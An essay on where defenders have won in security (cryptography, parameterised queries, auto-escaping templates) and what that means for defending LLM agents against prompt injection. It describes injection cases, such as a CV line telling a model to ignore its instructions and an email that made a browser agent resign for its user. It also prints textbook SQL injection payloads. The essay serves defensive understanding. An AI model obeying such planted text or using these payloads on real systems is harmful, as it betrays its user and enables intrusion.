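# Where defenders won in computer security, and what that means for language model agents

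## The claim that attackers always win

People in computer security often say that the attacker always wins in the end, and they now say it above all about language model agents. An agent is a large language model (LLM) that pursues a task by calling tools, such as email, a web browser or a command shell, and acting on the results. Unlike a chatbot, which only produces text for a person to read, an agent can send messages, approve payments or delete files, so whoever controls what the model writes also controls those tools.

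Prompt injection is a common way to get that control. The attacker places text in content that the model will read, worded so that the model follows the attacker's instructions instead of its user's. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C's December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), gives the example of a recruiter who instructs a model to score whether each CV meets the job's requirements. One candidate has hidden a line in a CV that tells the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve the CV for interview. The candidate needs no access to the recruiter's system, because the system itself passes the CV to the model. In real cases, according to The Record's *UK intelligence warns AI 'prompt injection' attacks might never go away*, attackers have used the technique to uncover the hidden instructions of Microsoft's New Bing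 search engine and to steal secrets through GitHub's Copilot, a coding assistant.

Attacks on agents can do more damage. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes a test of the agent in the company's web browser. An automated attacker planted an email in a user's inbox containing instructions to send a resignation letter to the user's chief executive. When the user later asked for an out-of-office reply, the agent came across the email, followed the instructions and resigned on the user's behalf.

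A vulnerability class is a group of flaws with the same cause. One example is SQL injection, in which text that a visitor types into a web form runs as a command to the site's database. Another is memory corruption, in which a program writes outside the memory meant for it. A security boundary is a line across which a system limits what one side may do to the other. Microsoft's published criteria for Windows list ten of them, including the boundary between ordinary programs and the kernel, the core of the operating system.

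The claim that attackers always win rests on three arguments. An attacker needs only one hole, while the defender must close all of them. The attacker can also choose an attack after seeing the defence. Finally, a language model has no internal separation between instructions and data.

### One hole is enough

In *Why Information Security is Hard* (2001), the Cambridge computer scientist Ross Anderson used a numerical example to show why defence is hard when an attacker needs only one hole. Suppose that a product as large as Windows 2000 contains a million bugs, each of which takes an average of a billion hours of testing to find. Paddy, who wants to break into a British Army computer, has a day job and can test for 1,000 hours a year. Brian, who defends the computer, has the source code, dozens of PhDs and 10 million hours of testing a year. Anderson calculated that after a year Paddy would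 have found one bug and Brian 100,000, but that there would be only a 10% chance that Brian had found Paddy's bug. (The stated rates give Brian 10,000 bugs and a 1% chance, which strengthens the argument.) Anderson concluded that attack is easier than defence.

Anderson also saw two ways out, both consistent with the arithmetic. If half of the critical bugs are stack overflows, a form of memory corruption, a new compiler might remove them all at once. Designers could also shrink the trusted computing base, meaning the parts of a system that must be correct for its security to hold, until testers can find every bug in it. Anderson doubted that designers would do this soon, because platform vendors have an incentive to attract application developers, and a minimal base makes those developers' work harder.

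In *The worst truism in information security*, the security practitioner Alex Gaynor rejects the saying that an attacker needs to find only one hole. Under that saying, a system is either secure or insecure, and since every large system has flaws, none would count as secure. Skilled practitioners ask instead what an attack costs and what it yields. A sandbox, which confines a program to a small set of permitted actions, can force the attacker to chain several flaws together. Monitoring reverses the saying, because one mistake can expose the intruder. On Gaynor's account, defenders win when breaking in costs more than it is worth. Defenders can misjudge that balance, since a defence designed to stop amateurs will not hold against a state intelligence service.

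How the balance moves when both sides invest more is a research question of its own. Garfinkel and Dafoe (2019), in *How does the offense-defense balance scale?*, illustrate it with a country that builds a wall along its border. An attacker can walk around half a wall, so a complete wall is worth much more than twice as much. For software they model a system with N flaws, in which the attacker's effort A and the defender's effort D each turn up flaws at random. The number of flaws that the attacker can expect to find and the defender to miss is

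S = min(N, A) × (N − min(N, D)) / N

If there are ten flaws and both sides spend equal effort, the attacker has on average 0.9 usable flaws at one unit of effort each, 2.5 at five units, 1.6 at eight and none at ten. More effort on both sides therefore helps the attacker at first, while the two sides are finding different flaws, and helps the defender later, once the defender misses few flaws. Anderson's story is at the low end of this curve, because the formula also gives 0.9 for a million flaws when Paddy finds one and Brian finds 100,000.

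The model rests on the assumptions that nobody adds new flaws in the meantime and that each side's discoveries are independent of the other's. Garfinkel and Dafoe note that automated tools might lead both sides to the same flaws, which would favour the defender, but they call the short-term effect of automation ambiguous. *Uplifted Attackers, Human Defenders* (2025) adds that the later, defensive part of the curve helps only organisations that invest in defence. The *International AI Safety Report 2026* (2026) describes how to steer the balance towards safety as an open question.

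Prompt injection also fits poorly with the model's assumption that the number of flaws is fixed. David C writes that an attacker can rephrase an injection in infinitely many ways. As N grows without limit, S approaches A, so the defender's finds stop mattering and the attacker keeps all of theirs. This overstates the difficulty somewhat, since one round of retraining may block many phrasings together. Still, it is a reason to prefer defences that remove a whole class of flaws, or that limit what a successful attacker can reach, over defences that fix flaws one at a time.

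### The attacker moves second

A defender has to commit to a design, which the attacker can then study. An adaptive attacker knows how the defence works and tailors the attack to it. Security researchers have assumed this kind of attacker since Auguste Kerckhoffs wrote on the subject in 1883.

Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) argue in *The Attacker Moves Second* that research on language models has neglected this lesson. Researchers commonly test a defence against a fixed list of old attack texts, or against a general-purpose search program with a small computing budget. A good result on such a test shows little about how the defence would fare against an attacker who writes new texts for it. The team, from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind and other organisations, adapted its attacks to 12 published defences and reached attack success rates above 90% against most of them. Most of the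 12 had rates near zero in their original evaluations. An attack success rate is the share of attack attempts, or of attacked tasks, in which the attacker reaches the goal, and it means little without a description of the attacker.

Some of the 12 defences were against jailbreaks, in which the user tries to get around the model designer's rules. In prompt injection, an outsider turns the system against its user, and can make it steal the user's private data, delete files or send emails that the user never meant to send.

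Moving second helps an attacker only if some attack can succeed. Cryptographers also assume that the attacker knows the design, and they define security against every possible attacker within some limit on computing power. Nasr and colleagues accept defences of this kind, provided that breaking them takes more computation than current technology allows. A defence that a cluster of ordinary processors can break in a day does not qualify. Letting the attacker move second therefore sets a demanding standard for testing, but it does not show that every defence will fail.

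### No line between instructions and data

The argument particular to language models appears in its clearest form in David C's post, and it runs as follows.

1. SQL injection, cross-site scripting (an attacker's script runs in another visitor's browser) and buffer overflows (a form of memory corruption) have the same underlying cause. A system handles data as if it were instructions.
2. In each case the system processes instructions and data differently. In a database, an instruction is something the engine does, and data is something it stores or uses in a query.
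3. A fix can therefore enforce the difference. With parameterised queries, the database engine can never interpret a visitor's input as an instruction.
4. An LLM offers no such difference to enforce. The developer's instructions and the stranger's CV form a single run of tokens, or word fragments, and the model predicts the most likely next one.
5. Detecting injections, training models to give priority to instructions, and marking which text is data all lay a distinction over a technology that lacks it.

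David C concludes that prompt injection may never be totally mitigated in the way that SQL injection can be. The wording is rightly cautious ("very possible", "a good chance"), because the conclusion does not follow strictly from the premises. A model with no built-in distinction between instructions and data might still learn one. But it would learn a statistical tendency, and an adaptive attacker looks for inputs on which that tendency fails, which gives the argument much of its force.

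OpenAI similarly considers prompt injection, like scams aimed at people, "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'". *Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns* (Poireault, 2026) reports that in June 2026 Ariel Fogel of OWASP, an organisation that ranks software security risks, called it an "unresolved problem" within the architecture of generative AI.

David C suggests that designers stop treating prompt injection as a form of code injection and think of the model as an "inherently confusable deputy". A confused deputy is a privileged program that a less privileged party tricks into misusing its authority. The term dates to 1988, when *The Confused Deputy* by Norm Hardy told a nearly true story from Tymshare, which sold computer time. A compiler there had permission to write in its own directory, which held its usage statistics and the company's billing file. Users could name a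 file to receive the compiler's debugging output, and one user gave the name of the billing file. The operating system checked the compiler's permission and allowed the write, and the company lost its billing information.

Hardy concluded that the compiler held authority from both the user and the system, but had no way to state which it was using for a particular file. His remedy was a capability, a token that both identifies a file and carries permission to write to it. Users would pass the compiler a capability for the output file, and users with no right to the billing file would have no capability for it. This works because the compiler's code keeps the two files separate, sending statistics to one and debugging output to the other. A language model has no equally reliable way to separate its user's wishes from a stranger's text, so David C regards the confusion as inherent.

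### Safeguards outside the model

These fixes are all inside the model, but the same NCSC post tells designers to concentrate on "deterministic (non-LLM) safeguards that constrain the actions of the system", meaning ordinary code that applies the same rule however an attacker words the text. David C quotes a rule from an online exchange between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista: when a model processes information from some party, its privileges drop to those of that party. No company would give a random outsider access to its payment system, so a model that reads email from outsiders should not have that access either. An injected email may still fool the model, but the model will have no way to pay anyone. According to The Record, the rule's originator acknowledged that it would "massively limit the capabilities of AI agents".

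Government agencies have since given similar advice. The Australian Cyber Security Centre's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), written by six agencies from five countries, calls for strict adherence to least privilege, which means giving each component only the access its task needs. One of its scenarios is a modern confused deputy. An organisation gives a procurement agent broad access to its financial systems, email and contracts. An attacker compromises a minor tool that the agent uses, then uses the agent to change contracts and approve payments. The logs look legitimate because a trusted agent performed every action. In August 2026 the NCSC again urged sandboxing, oversight and tight access controls for agents (Mascellino, 2026, *NCSC Urges Stronger Controls for Agentic AI Systems*).

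The CV example shows a limit of these safeguards. A candidate who hides a line of text can cause a wrong score without misusing a tool or crossing a boundary, because the recruiter asked the system for a score. Code around the model can require a person's approval before the system invites anyone to interview, but it cannot ensure that the score is right. David C advises that an LLM may be the wrong choice for systems that cannot tolerate the remaining risk.

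### What counts as a win

If winning means a system without flaws, no defender has ever won. Gaynor's economic view suggests a more useful standard, with three tests:

- The attack class becomes rare or unaffordable wherever people use the defence.
- This holds against adaptive attackers.
- It lasts without a fresh fix for each new attack.

The last test excludes much honest work. OpenAI uses an automated attacker to search for new kinds of prompt injection, retrains its agent against the attacks it finds, and sends users the updated agent. OpenAI reports that it has discovered new attack strategies this way before they appeared in the wild. The process may well reduce the risk to users, but the protection depends on OpenAI continuing to find attacks before outsiders do.

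The tests also help separate hard barriers from friction. A hard barrier makes an attack impossible unless a stated assumption fails, while friction makes an attack slower or more tedious. Microsoft draws a similar line in Windows. It intends to issue updates for sufficiently severe flaws that breach a security boundary. By default it issues none for ways around its "defense-in-depth" features, such as arranging memory randomly so that attackers cannot predict where things are, because these features may have limits by design. Friction can pass the test of cost for a time and then fail it when attackers get better tools. Hard barriers also need maintenance, because programmers make mistakes in building them. A defence that needs such repairs can still count as a win, so long as it does not depend on a steady supply of them to keep up with new attacks.

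A win in this sense covers only one class of attack. A website that blocks SQL injection is still open to someone who has stolen an administrator's password.

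## Cryptography

Cryptography protects information with mathematics, so that someone who intercepts a message cannot read it or change it unnoticed. It is the strongest example of a defence that won. When a browser connects to a bank, it encrypts the traffic in milliseconds. The algorithms are public, yet nobody has published a practical way to break them. Their security became less certain in 2026, when AI models began to find weaknesses in the mathematics behind cryptography, including that of some algorithms now in use.

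### The cost of a longer key

A symmetric cipher uses the same secret key to encrypt and decrypt. If the key is n bits long, there are 2^n possible keys, and an attacker with no better method can try them one by one. Each added bit doubles the attacker's work but adds very little to the user's. The Advanced Encryption Standard (AES), the most widely used symmetric cipher, scrambles data in repeated steps called rounds. It uses 10 rounds with a 128-bit key and 14 with a 256-bit key, so the longer key requires about 40% more computation from the user but gives the attacker 2^128 times as many keys to try.

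Suppose an attacker can test 10^18 keys a second. The Data Encryption Standard (DES), which the US government adopted in 1977, has 56-bit keys, and the attacker can try all 2^56 of them (about 7.2 × 10^16) in 0.07 seconds. A 128-bit AES key is little more than twice as long, but there are 3.4 × 10^38 such keys. Trying them all would take about 10^13 years, nearly 800 times the age of the universe. A machine a thousand times as fast would still need about ten billion years.

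Critics knew from the start that the DES key was too short. Whitfield Diffie and Martin Hellman warned in 1977 that a $20 million machine could find a DES key in about a day. In 1998 the Electronic Frontier Foundation, a digital rights group, built a DES-cracking machine for less than $250,000. It tested about 90 billion keys a second and found the key to a challenge message in 56 hours; a full search would have taken about nine days. Users at first ran DES three times with different keys, and later moved to AES.

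The exponential difficulty of guessing a key protects the defender only while guessing is the attacker's best method. A flaw in a cipher's design can allow a faster attack, and much of modern cryptography aims to rule such attacks out.

### Security against every efficient attacker

In 1883 the Dutch linguist Auguste Kerckhoffs wrote that a military cipher should stay secure even if the enemy captures everything except the key. Cryptographers still follow Kerckhoffs's principle because users can replace a leaked key in moments, while a new design takes years. Outsiders can also find flaws in a public design before an enemy does.

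In the 1980s Shafi Goldwasser and Silvio Micali turned this attitude into precise definitions. A common one takes the form of a game:

1. The attacker chooses two messages of equal length.
2. The defender picks one of them at random, encrypts it with a secret key and hands over the result.
3. The attacker guesses which message it was.

A blind guess is right half the time, so what counts is the attacker's advantage over guessing:

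Advantage = |Pr(correct guess) − 1/2|

The cipher is secure if every efficient attacker has a negligible advantage. "Efficient" means that the attacker's running time grows no faster than some fixed power of the key length, and "negligible" means that the advantage shrinks faster than one divided by any such power. Stronger versions of the definition also let the attacker ask for encryptions of any other messages. The definition covers attacks that nobody has invented yet because it doesn't specify a method of attack. Nasr and colleagues criticised research on language models for testing against a fixed list of old attacks, which covers only the attacks on that list.

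No experiment can test a cipher against every efficient attacker, so cryptographers use proofs by reduction, which show that anyone who broke the cipher could also solve a problem believed to be hard. Take a cipher that stretches a short key into a long, random-looking string, called the pad, and combines the pad with the message bit by bit. The proof for a single message runs as follows.

1. Suppose that an efficient attacker wins the game with probability 1/2 + ε.
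2. Write a tester, a program that receives a string and must decide whether it is truly random or came from the stretching algorithm. The tester uses the string as the pad, encrypts one of the attacker's two messages at random, and records whether the attacker guesses correctly.
3. If the string is truly random, the encrypted message carries no information about the original, and the attacker is right exactly half the time.
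4. If the string came from the algorithm, the attacker is right with probability 1/2 + ε.
5. The tester can therefore tell the two kinds of string apart with advantage ε.

If no efficient program can tell the stretching algorithm's output from random bits, no efficient attacker can break the cipher. The proof depends on that one narrow assumption, so researchers can concentrate their attacks on it.

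### Open competitions and unproved assumptions

Cryptographers test such assumptions mainly through public competitions. The US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) invited designs for a successor to DES in 1997 and accepted 15 candidates. The competing teams tried to break one another's designs, as did other cryptographers, and they published what they found. NIST named five finalists in 1999, chose a design by the Belgian cryptographers Joan Daemen and Vincent Rijmen in 2000, and issued it as AES in 2001. Cryptographers trust AES because those attacks, and about 25 years of later ones, have failed to break it.

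Despite that evidence, nobody has proved that breaking AES is hard, or that any of the problems behind widely used encryption are hard. A proof would have to settle the P versus NP problem, which asks whether computers can quickly solve every problem whose solutions they can quickly check. If they can, no cipher with keys much shorter than its messages meets the definition above. The problem remains open, although *The world is not ending* (Caputo, Pantazi and Kay, 2026) describes rumours that AI models were close to solving it.

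In late October 2026 OpenAI announced a refutation, found by its model, of a famous assumption about hardness called the Exponential Time Hypothesis. The hypothesis holds, roughly, that finding a solution to a set of simple logical conditions takes exponential time in the worst case. The announced refutation has had no practical effect so far. Szeider calculated in *OpenAI's claimed refutation of ETH* that the new algorithm is still an exhaustive search on every input with fewer than 2^131071 variables and clauses, a number with more than 39,000 digits. No computer could store an input that large. An assumption about how hard problems become as they grow without limit can therefore be false while keys of ordinary size stay safe.

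Public-key cryptography needs riskier assumptions than symmetric ciphers. It lets two strangers agree on a secret key over an open line, and lets a website prove its identity with a digital signature. For this, designers need an operation that is easy to perform and hard to reverse, except for someone who holds a secret. Only a few mathematical problems are known to provide one, and the structure that makes them useful may also help an attacker. RSA, one of the oldest schemes, relies on the difficulty of factoring large numbers. Peter Shor showed in 1994 that a large quantum computer could factor them efficiently, and could break the newer elliptic-curve schemes too. Nobody has built such a computer, but in 2016 NIST began a second competition, for post-quantum algorithms that should resist one.

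### SIKE, HAWK and seven rounds of AES

SIKE, a candidate in that competition, was a method for agreeing on keys. Its security rested on the difficulty of finding a hidden path between two elliptic curves when the attacker also sees where the path sends certain points. In July 2022 NIST kept SIKE for a fourth round of review. Within weeks Wouter Castryck and Thomas Decru, of KU Leuven in Belgium, showed how to find the path using those points and a theorem from 1997. Breaking SIKE took an hour on a laptop, according to Anthropic's *Discovering cryptographic weaknesses with Claude* (2026). The attack broke even the largest proposed key size within a day, so longer keys did not solve the problem.

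The collapse did little damage. Google and Cloudflare had tested SIKE on live browser connections in 2019, but they combined it with an established elliptic-curve method, so an eavesdropper would have had to break both.

HAWK, a post-quantum signature scheme that NIST was considering for standardisation, failed less severely. It had survived two rounds of expert review over two years when, in July 2026, Anthropic published an attack that its researcher had developed with Claude Mythos Preview, a model the company had announced in April. HAWK relies on the difficulty of matching two different descriptions of the same lattice, a regular grid of points in many dimensions. Earlier work had proved that an attacker could exploit a certain kind of symmetry in the lattice if there were an efficient way to find it. Nobody had established whether HAWK's lattice had a symmetry that an attacker could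 find efficiently until Mythos Preview found one.

For the smallest version, HAWK-256, the expected number of steps needed to recover a key fell from 2^64 to 2^38, a factor of about 67 million. The attack still takes exponential time, so HAWK's designers could restore the lost security by doubling the key size, but the scheme would lose much of its appeal, which was its efficiency. No deployed system used HAWK, and the attack does not work on other lattice schemes.

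Finding, developing and checking the attack took about 60 hours and roughly $100,000 of computing. The lead researcher knew theoretical computer science but was not an expert on lattices, and mostly managed the project while several copies of the model worked on the mathematics. One copy rejected the decisive idea as infeasible before another found how to use it.

Mythos Preview found a faster attack on a weakened version of AES, with 7 of the 10 rounds. Cryptographers study such versions to see how much security margin the full cipher has. The best earlier attacks of this type looked values up in a large table of intermediate results and had to try 256 possibilities at one stage. The model devised a fingerprint of the data that is the same for all 256, so the attack no longer has to try each one. Computing the fingerprint takes extra work, but further savings made the whole attack 200 to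 800 times faster than the previous best.

None of this makes an attack on AES practical. The method needs 2^105 chosen messages encrypted under the unknown key. Collecting them at 10^18 a second would take more than a million years, and the full cipher has three more rounds than the version attacked. Mythos Preview improved more on earlier attacks against LEA, a cipher for small devices. The best previous attack on 13 of LEA's 24 rounds required 2^98 pairs of messages. The model's attack uses fewer than 2^30 messages and runs in under an hour on a desktop computer, but it does not break the full 24-round cipher.

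The model found the AES attack in a week, but two researchers needed nearly a month to become confident it was correct. The HAWK attack was easier to check because anyone can run it and see whether it recovers the key.

### The disclosures of December 2026

Anthropic's next results concerned standards already in use. Chrome, Safari, Signal and iMessage all include ML-KEM, NIST's post-quantum method for agreeing on keys (Ryan, 2026, *Answering your questions about Anthropic's lattice cryptography results*). ML-KEM and the signature standard ML-DSA are faster because they use lattices with extra algebraic structure. On 30 November Anthropic published a quantum algorithm that exploits this structure.

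In the Cryptography Incident Review Group's *Initial Assessment of Anthropic’s Findings on Lattice Cryptography* (2026), the outside cryptographers who reviewed the work call its significance asymptotic. For a fixed number of structured components, each of size n, the attack takes about n^(c log n) steps for some constant c. With c = 1 and logarithms to base 2, doubling n from 256 to 512 would raise the number of steps from 2^64 to 2^81, whereas an attack that takes 2^n steps would go from 2^256 to 2^512. Security therefore grows much more slowly with n than cryptographers had believed.

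The actual number of operations is nowhere near these illustrative figures. CIRG estimates that even 2^1000 quantum operations would be far too few to break the smallest versions of ML-KEM and ML-DSA, so the attack is far less efficient than those already known. The standards also keep n at 256 and add components to increase security. Anthropic found no better attack for ordinary computers, and none at all on lattices without the extra structure. Ryan advises organisations that use the standards to change nothing for now, because a mistake during a hurried replacement is the greater danger.

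A separate warning followed on 2 December, when the US National Security Agency (NSA) and two other federal bodies announced that AI companies had disclosed discoveries affecting "some cryptographic systems currently in use". In a joint statement published by Anthropic (2026) on 5 December, Anthropic and OpenAI said that each had found weaknesses while testing unreleased models and had promptly reported them to the US government. According to the statement, the weaknesses lie in the mathematics of some of the cryptography that protects the internet, and have always been there. The findings do not affect NIST's post-quantum standards, which use different mathematics, and are unrelated to Anthropic's lattice papers, the companies said.

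The companies are withholding their methods and the exact dates of discovery. As of 6 December, neither they nor the government had named the algorithms or said whether the findings weaken them or break them completely (Johnson, 2026, *OpenAI, Anthropic say their nonpublic cryptography research presents no ‘immediate threat’*).

The advice that came with the warnings suggests that the discoveries concern older public-key algorithms, because those are the ones the post-quantum standards replace. No official has confirmed this. *Feds* (Matishak and Martin, 2026) reports that NSA guidance allows larger versions of established algorithms, such as RSA with 3,072-bit keys, as a stopgap for systems that cannot yet move to the new standards. That would be odd advice if the discoveries had broken RSA at every size, but the guidance does not describe any algorithm as broken or weakened.

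US and British officials played down the immediate danger. The three US bodies judged that the discoveries "do not present an immediate and widespread threat", although the NSA told those who run the most sensitive government networks to speed up their move at once. Ollie Whitehouse, chief technology officer of Britain's NCSC, confirmed that the discovery is new and valid and affects algorithms in use. He does not expect criminals to be able to exploit it (Martin, 2026, *UK cyber agency confirms new encryption threat, separate from Anthropic research*).

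Secrets that must last for decades are at risk before any practical attack exists, because an eavesdropper can record encrypted traffic today and decrypt it once a method becomes available. The NSA believes that adversaries are already collecting such traffic. Signatures are less urgent, because a future forger cannot go back and deceive someone who checked a signature years earlier.

The move to post-quantum cryptography was already under way. A US executive order of June 2026 requires the most important systems to use post-quantum methods for keys by 2030 and for signatures by 2031. *Execution of the Migration to Post-Quantum Cryptography* (Vought, 2026) put the order into effect across federal agencies, which have until 2035 to finish. The NCSC has kept its 2030 deadline for the highest-priority systems, and Whitehouse said that about 70% of UK internet traffic already has post-quantum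 protection. Anthropic and OpenAI have brought their own moves forward by several years, to the first half of 2027.

### How defenders keep the win

A mathematical weakness in deployed cryptography is worse than an ordinary software bug in some respects. It affects every product that uses the algorithm, however carefully the programmers worked, and it exposes recorded messages as well as new ones. Because the weakness has always existed, someone may have found it earlier and kept quiet, though no public evidence suggests this.

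Cryptographers have never treated any algorithm as permanently safe. They expect some to fail and try to find the flaws before they do harm. NIST publishes candidate algorithms so that people will attack them, and HAWK failed at that stage. Goldwasser argued in the week of the disclosures that slowing legitimate research would not stop adversaries from making similar discoveries. But early discovery helps little if attackers have equally good models and defenders are slow to act on what they learn.

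Security margins give defenders some of the time they need to act. An attacker who improves the attack on seven rounds of AES must still break ten, and CIRG recommends that organisations choose the highest security level that each application can support. Such margins work against gradual progress, like that seen with HAWK and AES, but would not have protected SIKE.

Because an algorithm can be broken suddenly, it should be easy to replace. Browsers and websites already agree on an algorithm at the start of each connection, so a software update can introduce a new one without a redesign of the web. NCSC's *Cryptographic agility* (2026) treats the ability to change algorithms as part of the move to post-quantum cryptography. Organisations can also use hybrids, which derive the key from two schemes with different mathematical foundations. Google and Cloudflare used SIKE in a hybrid of this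 kind.

Flexibility also creates risks. In 2015 researchers showed that an attacker could trick some browsers and websites into using weak 1990s algorithms that they still supported. Defenders therefore have to remove old methods as well as add new ones. Equipment with an algorithm fixed in hardware may need replacing, which the NSA warns could be costly.

Defenders in cryptography have been able to replace an algorithm about once in a generation instead of issuing a patch for every attack. DES lasted as a standard for more than two decades, and the move to AES ended the threat from key-guessing machines. Whether this pattern continues depends on how fast models find weaknesses and how fast defenders can replace algorithms. According to Anthropic, language models went in a single year from failing on the most basic ciphers to finding flaws that experts had missed. Large organisations take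 years to change an algorithm, so they could not keep up if models found a serious weakness in a deployed standard every year. The public record of 2026 is much milder: a candidate that failed before anyone deployed it, attacks on weakened ciphers, a theoretical result about lattices, and an undisclosed weakness for which replacements were ready. On that record, defenders still have the advantage, but with a smaller margin than before.

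### Faulty code and ways round encryption

A security proof for an algorithm does not cover the program that implements it. The Heartbleed flaw of 2014 was a missing length check in OpenSSL, a widely used cryptography library. It let attackers read fragments of a server's memory, sometimes including its secret keys, even though the encryption algorithms were sound. Other programs leak a key through the time they take to compute, and a mathematical definition of security covers this leak only if it explicitly includes timing.

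*Assessing Claude Mythos Preview's cybersecurity capabilities* (Carlini, Cheng and colleagues, 2026) reports that Mythos Preview also found flaws of this sort in the world's most popular cryptography libraries. The flaws were in code for AES-GCM (a way of using AES that also detects tampering) and for TLS and SSH, which protect web traffic and remote logins. Some would let an attacker forge the certificates that identify websites, or decrypt private communications. One critical flaw, which became public on the day of the report in April 2026, let an attacker bypass the certificate check.

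A leak harms users about equally whether the algorithm or the library is at fault, but a faulty library is much easier for defenders to deal with. Programmers can correct it without changing the algorithm, and correct libraries that use the same algorithm are unaffected. But such flaws keep appearing, so defenders' success with the mathematics does not extend to the software, and a cryptographic library needs the same protection against programming errors as any other program.

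Attackers can also bypass encryption without breaking it. In another of Carlini and colleagues' tests, Mythos Preview exploited a 17-year-old flaw in the file-sharing code of FreeBSD, an operating system. The exploit added the attacker's key to the list of keys accepted for administrator login. SSH would then have admitted the attacker and encrypted the session correctly. The model also built a web page that let the attacker write to the core of a visitor's operating system, where programs handle messages before encryption and after decryption.

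Encryption does not protect an agent against prompt injection. A secure connection can guarantee that an email reaches the agent exactly as the mail server sent it, including any instructions an attacker hid in the text.

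## SQL injection and cross-site scripting

Programming mistakes can undo sound cryptography, but defenders have learned to prevent some kinds almost entirely, including SQL injection and cross-site scripting (XSS). Both happen when a program inserts untrusted text into a database query written in SQL, or into a web page, and part of that text runs as code.

### A login query

Suppose that a website checks a login by asking its database for an account with the right name and password. A programmer has written the fixed parts of the query, and the program pastes in whatever the visitor types. If Alice logs in, the database receives this:

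```
SELECT * FROM accounts
WHERE name = 'alice' AND password = 'swordfish'
```

The database returns Alice's account if the password is right, and nothing if it is wrong. In 2006 Su and Wassermann, in *The Essence of Command Injection Attacks in Web Applications*, described an attacker who types `' OR 'a'='a` as the password. The same program now produces a different query:

```
SELECT * FROM accounts
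WHERE name = 'alice' AND password = '' OR 'a'='a'
```

The attacker's first apostrophe closes the password, leaving it empty. The database reads the next word, OR, as part of the query, and the programmer's closing apostrophe completes the final 'a'. SQL groups AND before OR, so the condition is now "the name is alice and the password is empty, or a equals a". That is true of every account, so the database returns them all, and a program that checks only whether the query returned any accounts lets the attacker in.

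Before a database runs a query, it parses the text into a tree that shows how the parts fit together. Alice's query has AND at the top, with two comparisons below it. The programmer meant visitors to supply only two values, but the attacker has changed the structure of the query, which now has OR at the top.

A parameterised query settles the structure before the input arrives. The programmer writes a template with a placeholder for each value:

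```
SELECT * FROM accounts
WHERE name = ? AND password = ?
```

1. The program sends the template to the database, which parses it into a tree with AND at the top and two gaps for values.
2. The program sends the visitor's name and password separately.
3. The database puts them in the gaps and runs the query without parsing it again.

If the attacker tries the same trick, the database looks for an account whose password is literally `' OR 'a'='a`, and finds none. The defence does not depend on what the input contains, so an attacker gains nothing by knowing how it works or by trying many variations. It is a hard barrier in the sense used earlier, and its main assumption is that the database software keeps the two steps separate. Some libraries only imitate parameterised queries by escaping the values and pasting them into the query text, which brings back the risks of escaping.

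### Trying to recognise bad input

Before parameterised queries became common, programmers mostly tried to reject dangerous input or make it harmless. Banning apostrophes also rejects valid names like O'Brien. Escaping lets the program accept these names. The program doubles each apostrophe in the input, and the database reads the pair as an ordinary character instead of the end of the text.

Both rules fail where the query expects a number, because SQL puts no quotation marks around numbers. In Su and Wassermann's example, an online shop shows customers their stored credit cards of a chosen type, and the program escapes every apostrophe. An attacker asks for card type `2 OR 1=1`, which contains no apostrophes, and gets every card number in the database.

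The escaping routine itself can also be flawed. In February 2025 the security company Rapid7 (2025) reported such a flaw in PostgreSQL, a popular database. According to PostgreSQL's advisory, *CVE-2025-1094*, the database's escaping routines failed to neutralise quotation marks in text that contained invalid characters. A program could therefore escape its input as the manual advised, pass it to PostgreSQL's command-line tool, and still run an attacker's command. SecurityWeek's *Rapid7 Flags New PostgreSQL Zero-Day Connected to BeyondTrust Exploitation* reports that the flaw appears to have been a critical part of attacks on BeyondTrust's remote support software, through which hackers compromised machines at the US Treasury.

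A web application firewall sits in front of a website and blocks requests that look like attacks. Organisations use these firewalls because they can protect software that nobody has time to rewrite. However, the firewall and the website may interpret the same request differently. *WAFFLED* (2025) reports 1,207 confirmed ways to get past five well-known firewalls, including those of Amazon, Microsoft and Cloudflare. The researchers looked for them by altering harmless parts of a request, such as its headers, until the firewall and the website interpreted it differently. They also found that more than 90% of websites accepted two common form encodings interchangeably, so an attacker can often pick the one that the firewall handles worse. Sassaman, Patterson and colleagues had already formalised this general technique as the "parse tree differential attack" in *Security Applications of Formal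 Language Theory* (2011).

Theory gives a reason to expect such leaks. *Defining Code-injection Attacks* (Ray and Ligatti, 2012) proved that, in a simplified version of SQL, any program that always copies some untrusted input unchanged into its queries is open to injection. It also showed that neither analysing the program in advance nor watching it from outside can detect these attacks precisely. A precise detector has to track the input through the running program, and a firewall has access only to the request. Firewalls can still stop crude attacks and give developers time to repair the flaw, but they slow attackers rather than reliably keeping them out.

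### Cross-site scripting

*If It's Not Secure, It Should Not Compile* (Wang, Bangert and Kern, 2021) explains cross-site scripting with a small search page. The page takes the visitor's search term from the web address and displays it under the words "You are searching". An attacker makes a link to the page in which the search term is HTML, the language of web pages, for an image that does not exist and a script to run if the image fails to load. When a victim follows the link, the browser inserts the search term into the page, fails to find the image and runs the script.

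Browsers normally prevent one website's scripts from reading another website's data. This script bypasses that rule because it runs as part of the search page. It can read the victim's private information there, including the cookies that keep the victim logged in, and send it to the attacker.

Cross-site scripting is harder to prevent than SQL injection, partly because a web page mixes several languages. Ordinary text, link addresses, styles and scripts each follow different rules, so the right way to escape input depends on where it will go. For example, replacing the angle brackets that mark HTML tags protects a paragraph of text, but not a link whose address begins with "javascript:", which tells the browser to run the rest as a script and needs no angle brackets. A programmer may also be handling text that a colleague's code stored months earlier, with no record of whether anyone escaped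 it.

Web pages have no exact equivalent of the database's placeholder, because the server sends the whole page as one stream of text. Templates that escape data automatically come close. The programmer writes the fixed parts of the page and leaves gaps for the rest. The template system parses the HTML around each gap, determines whether the gap holds text, a link or something else, and applies the matching escaping rule. This is still escaping, but software now does it every time. In the strict version that Google uses, programmers cannot switch the escaping off.

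Templates protect pages that the server builds, but on modern pages, scripts also change the page after it loads by calling the browser's own functions. Some of these functions will run any code in the text they receive. Attacks through them are called DOM-based XSS, after the Document Object Model, the browser's internal representation of a page. Wang and colleagues identified five kinds of dangerous function, based on whether the browser treats the text as a script, a link, the address of a file to load, HTML or a style.

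### Types that make the safe way compulsory

Telling programmers to use parameterised queries and templates does not guarantee that they will. *Secure by Design at Google* (Kern, 2024) states that a program must build the text of its SQL queries only from trustworthy pieces and supply all other values as parameters. This must hold for every possible input at every place where the program sends a query. A large program may contain thousands of such places, and one lapse is enough to make it vulnerable. Even text from the program's own database can be dangerous, since an attacker may have put it there earlier and another part of the program may then paste it into a query.

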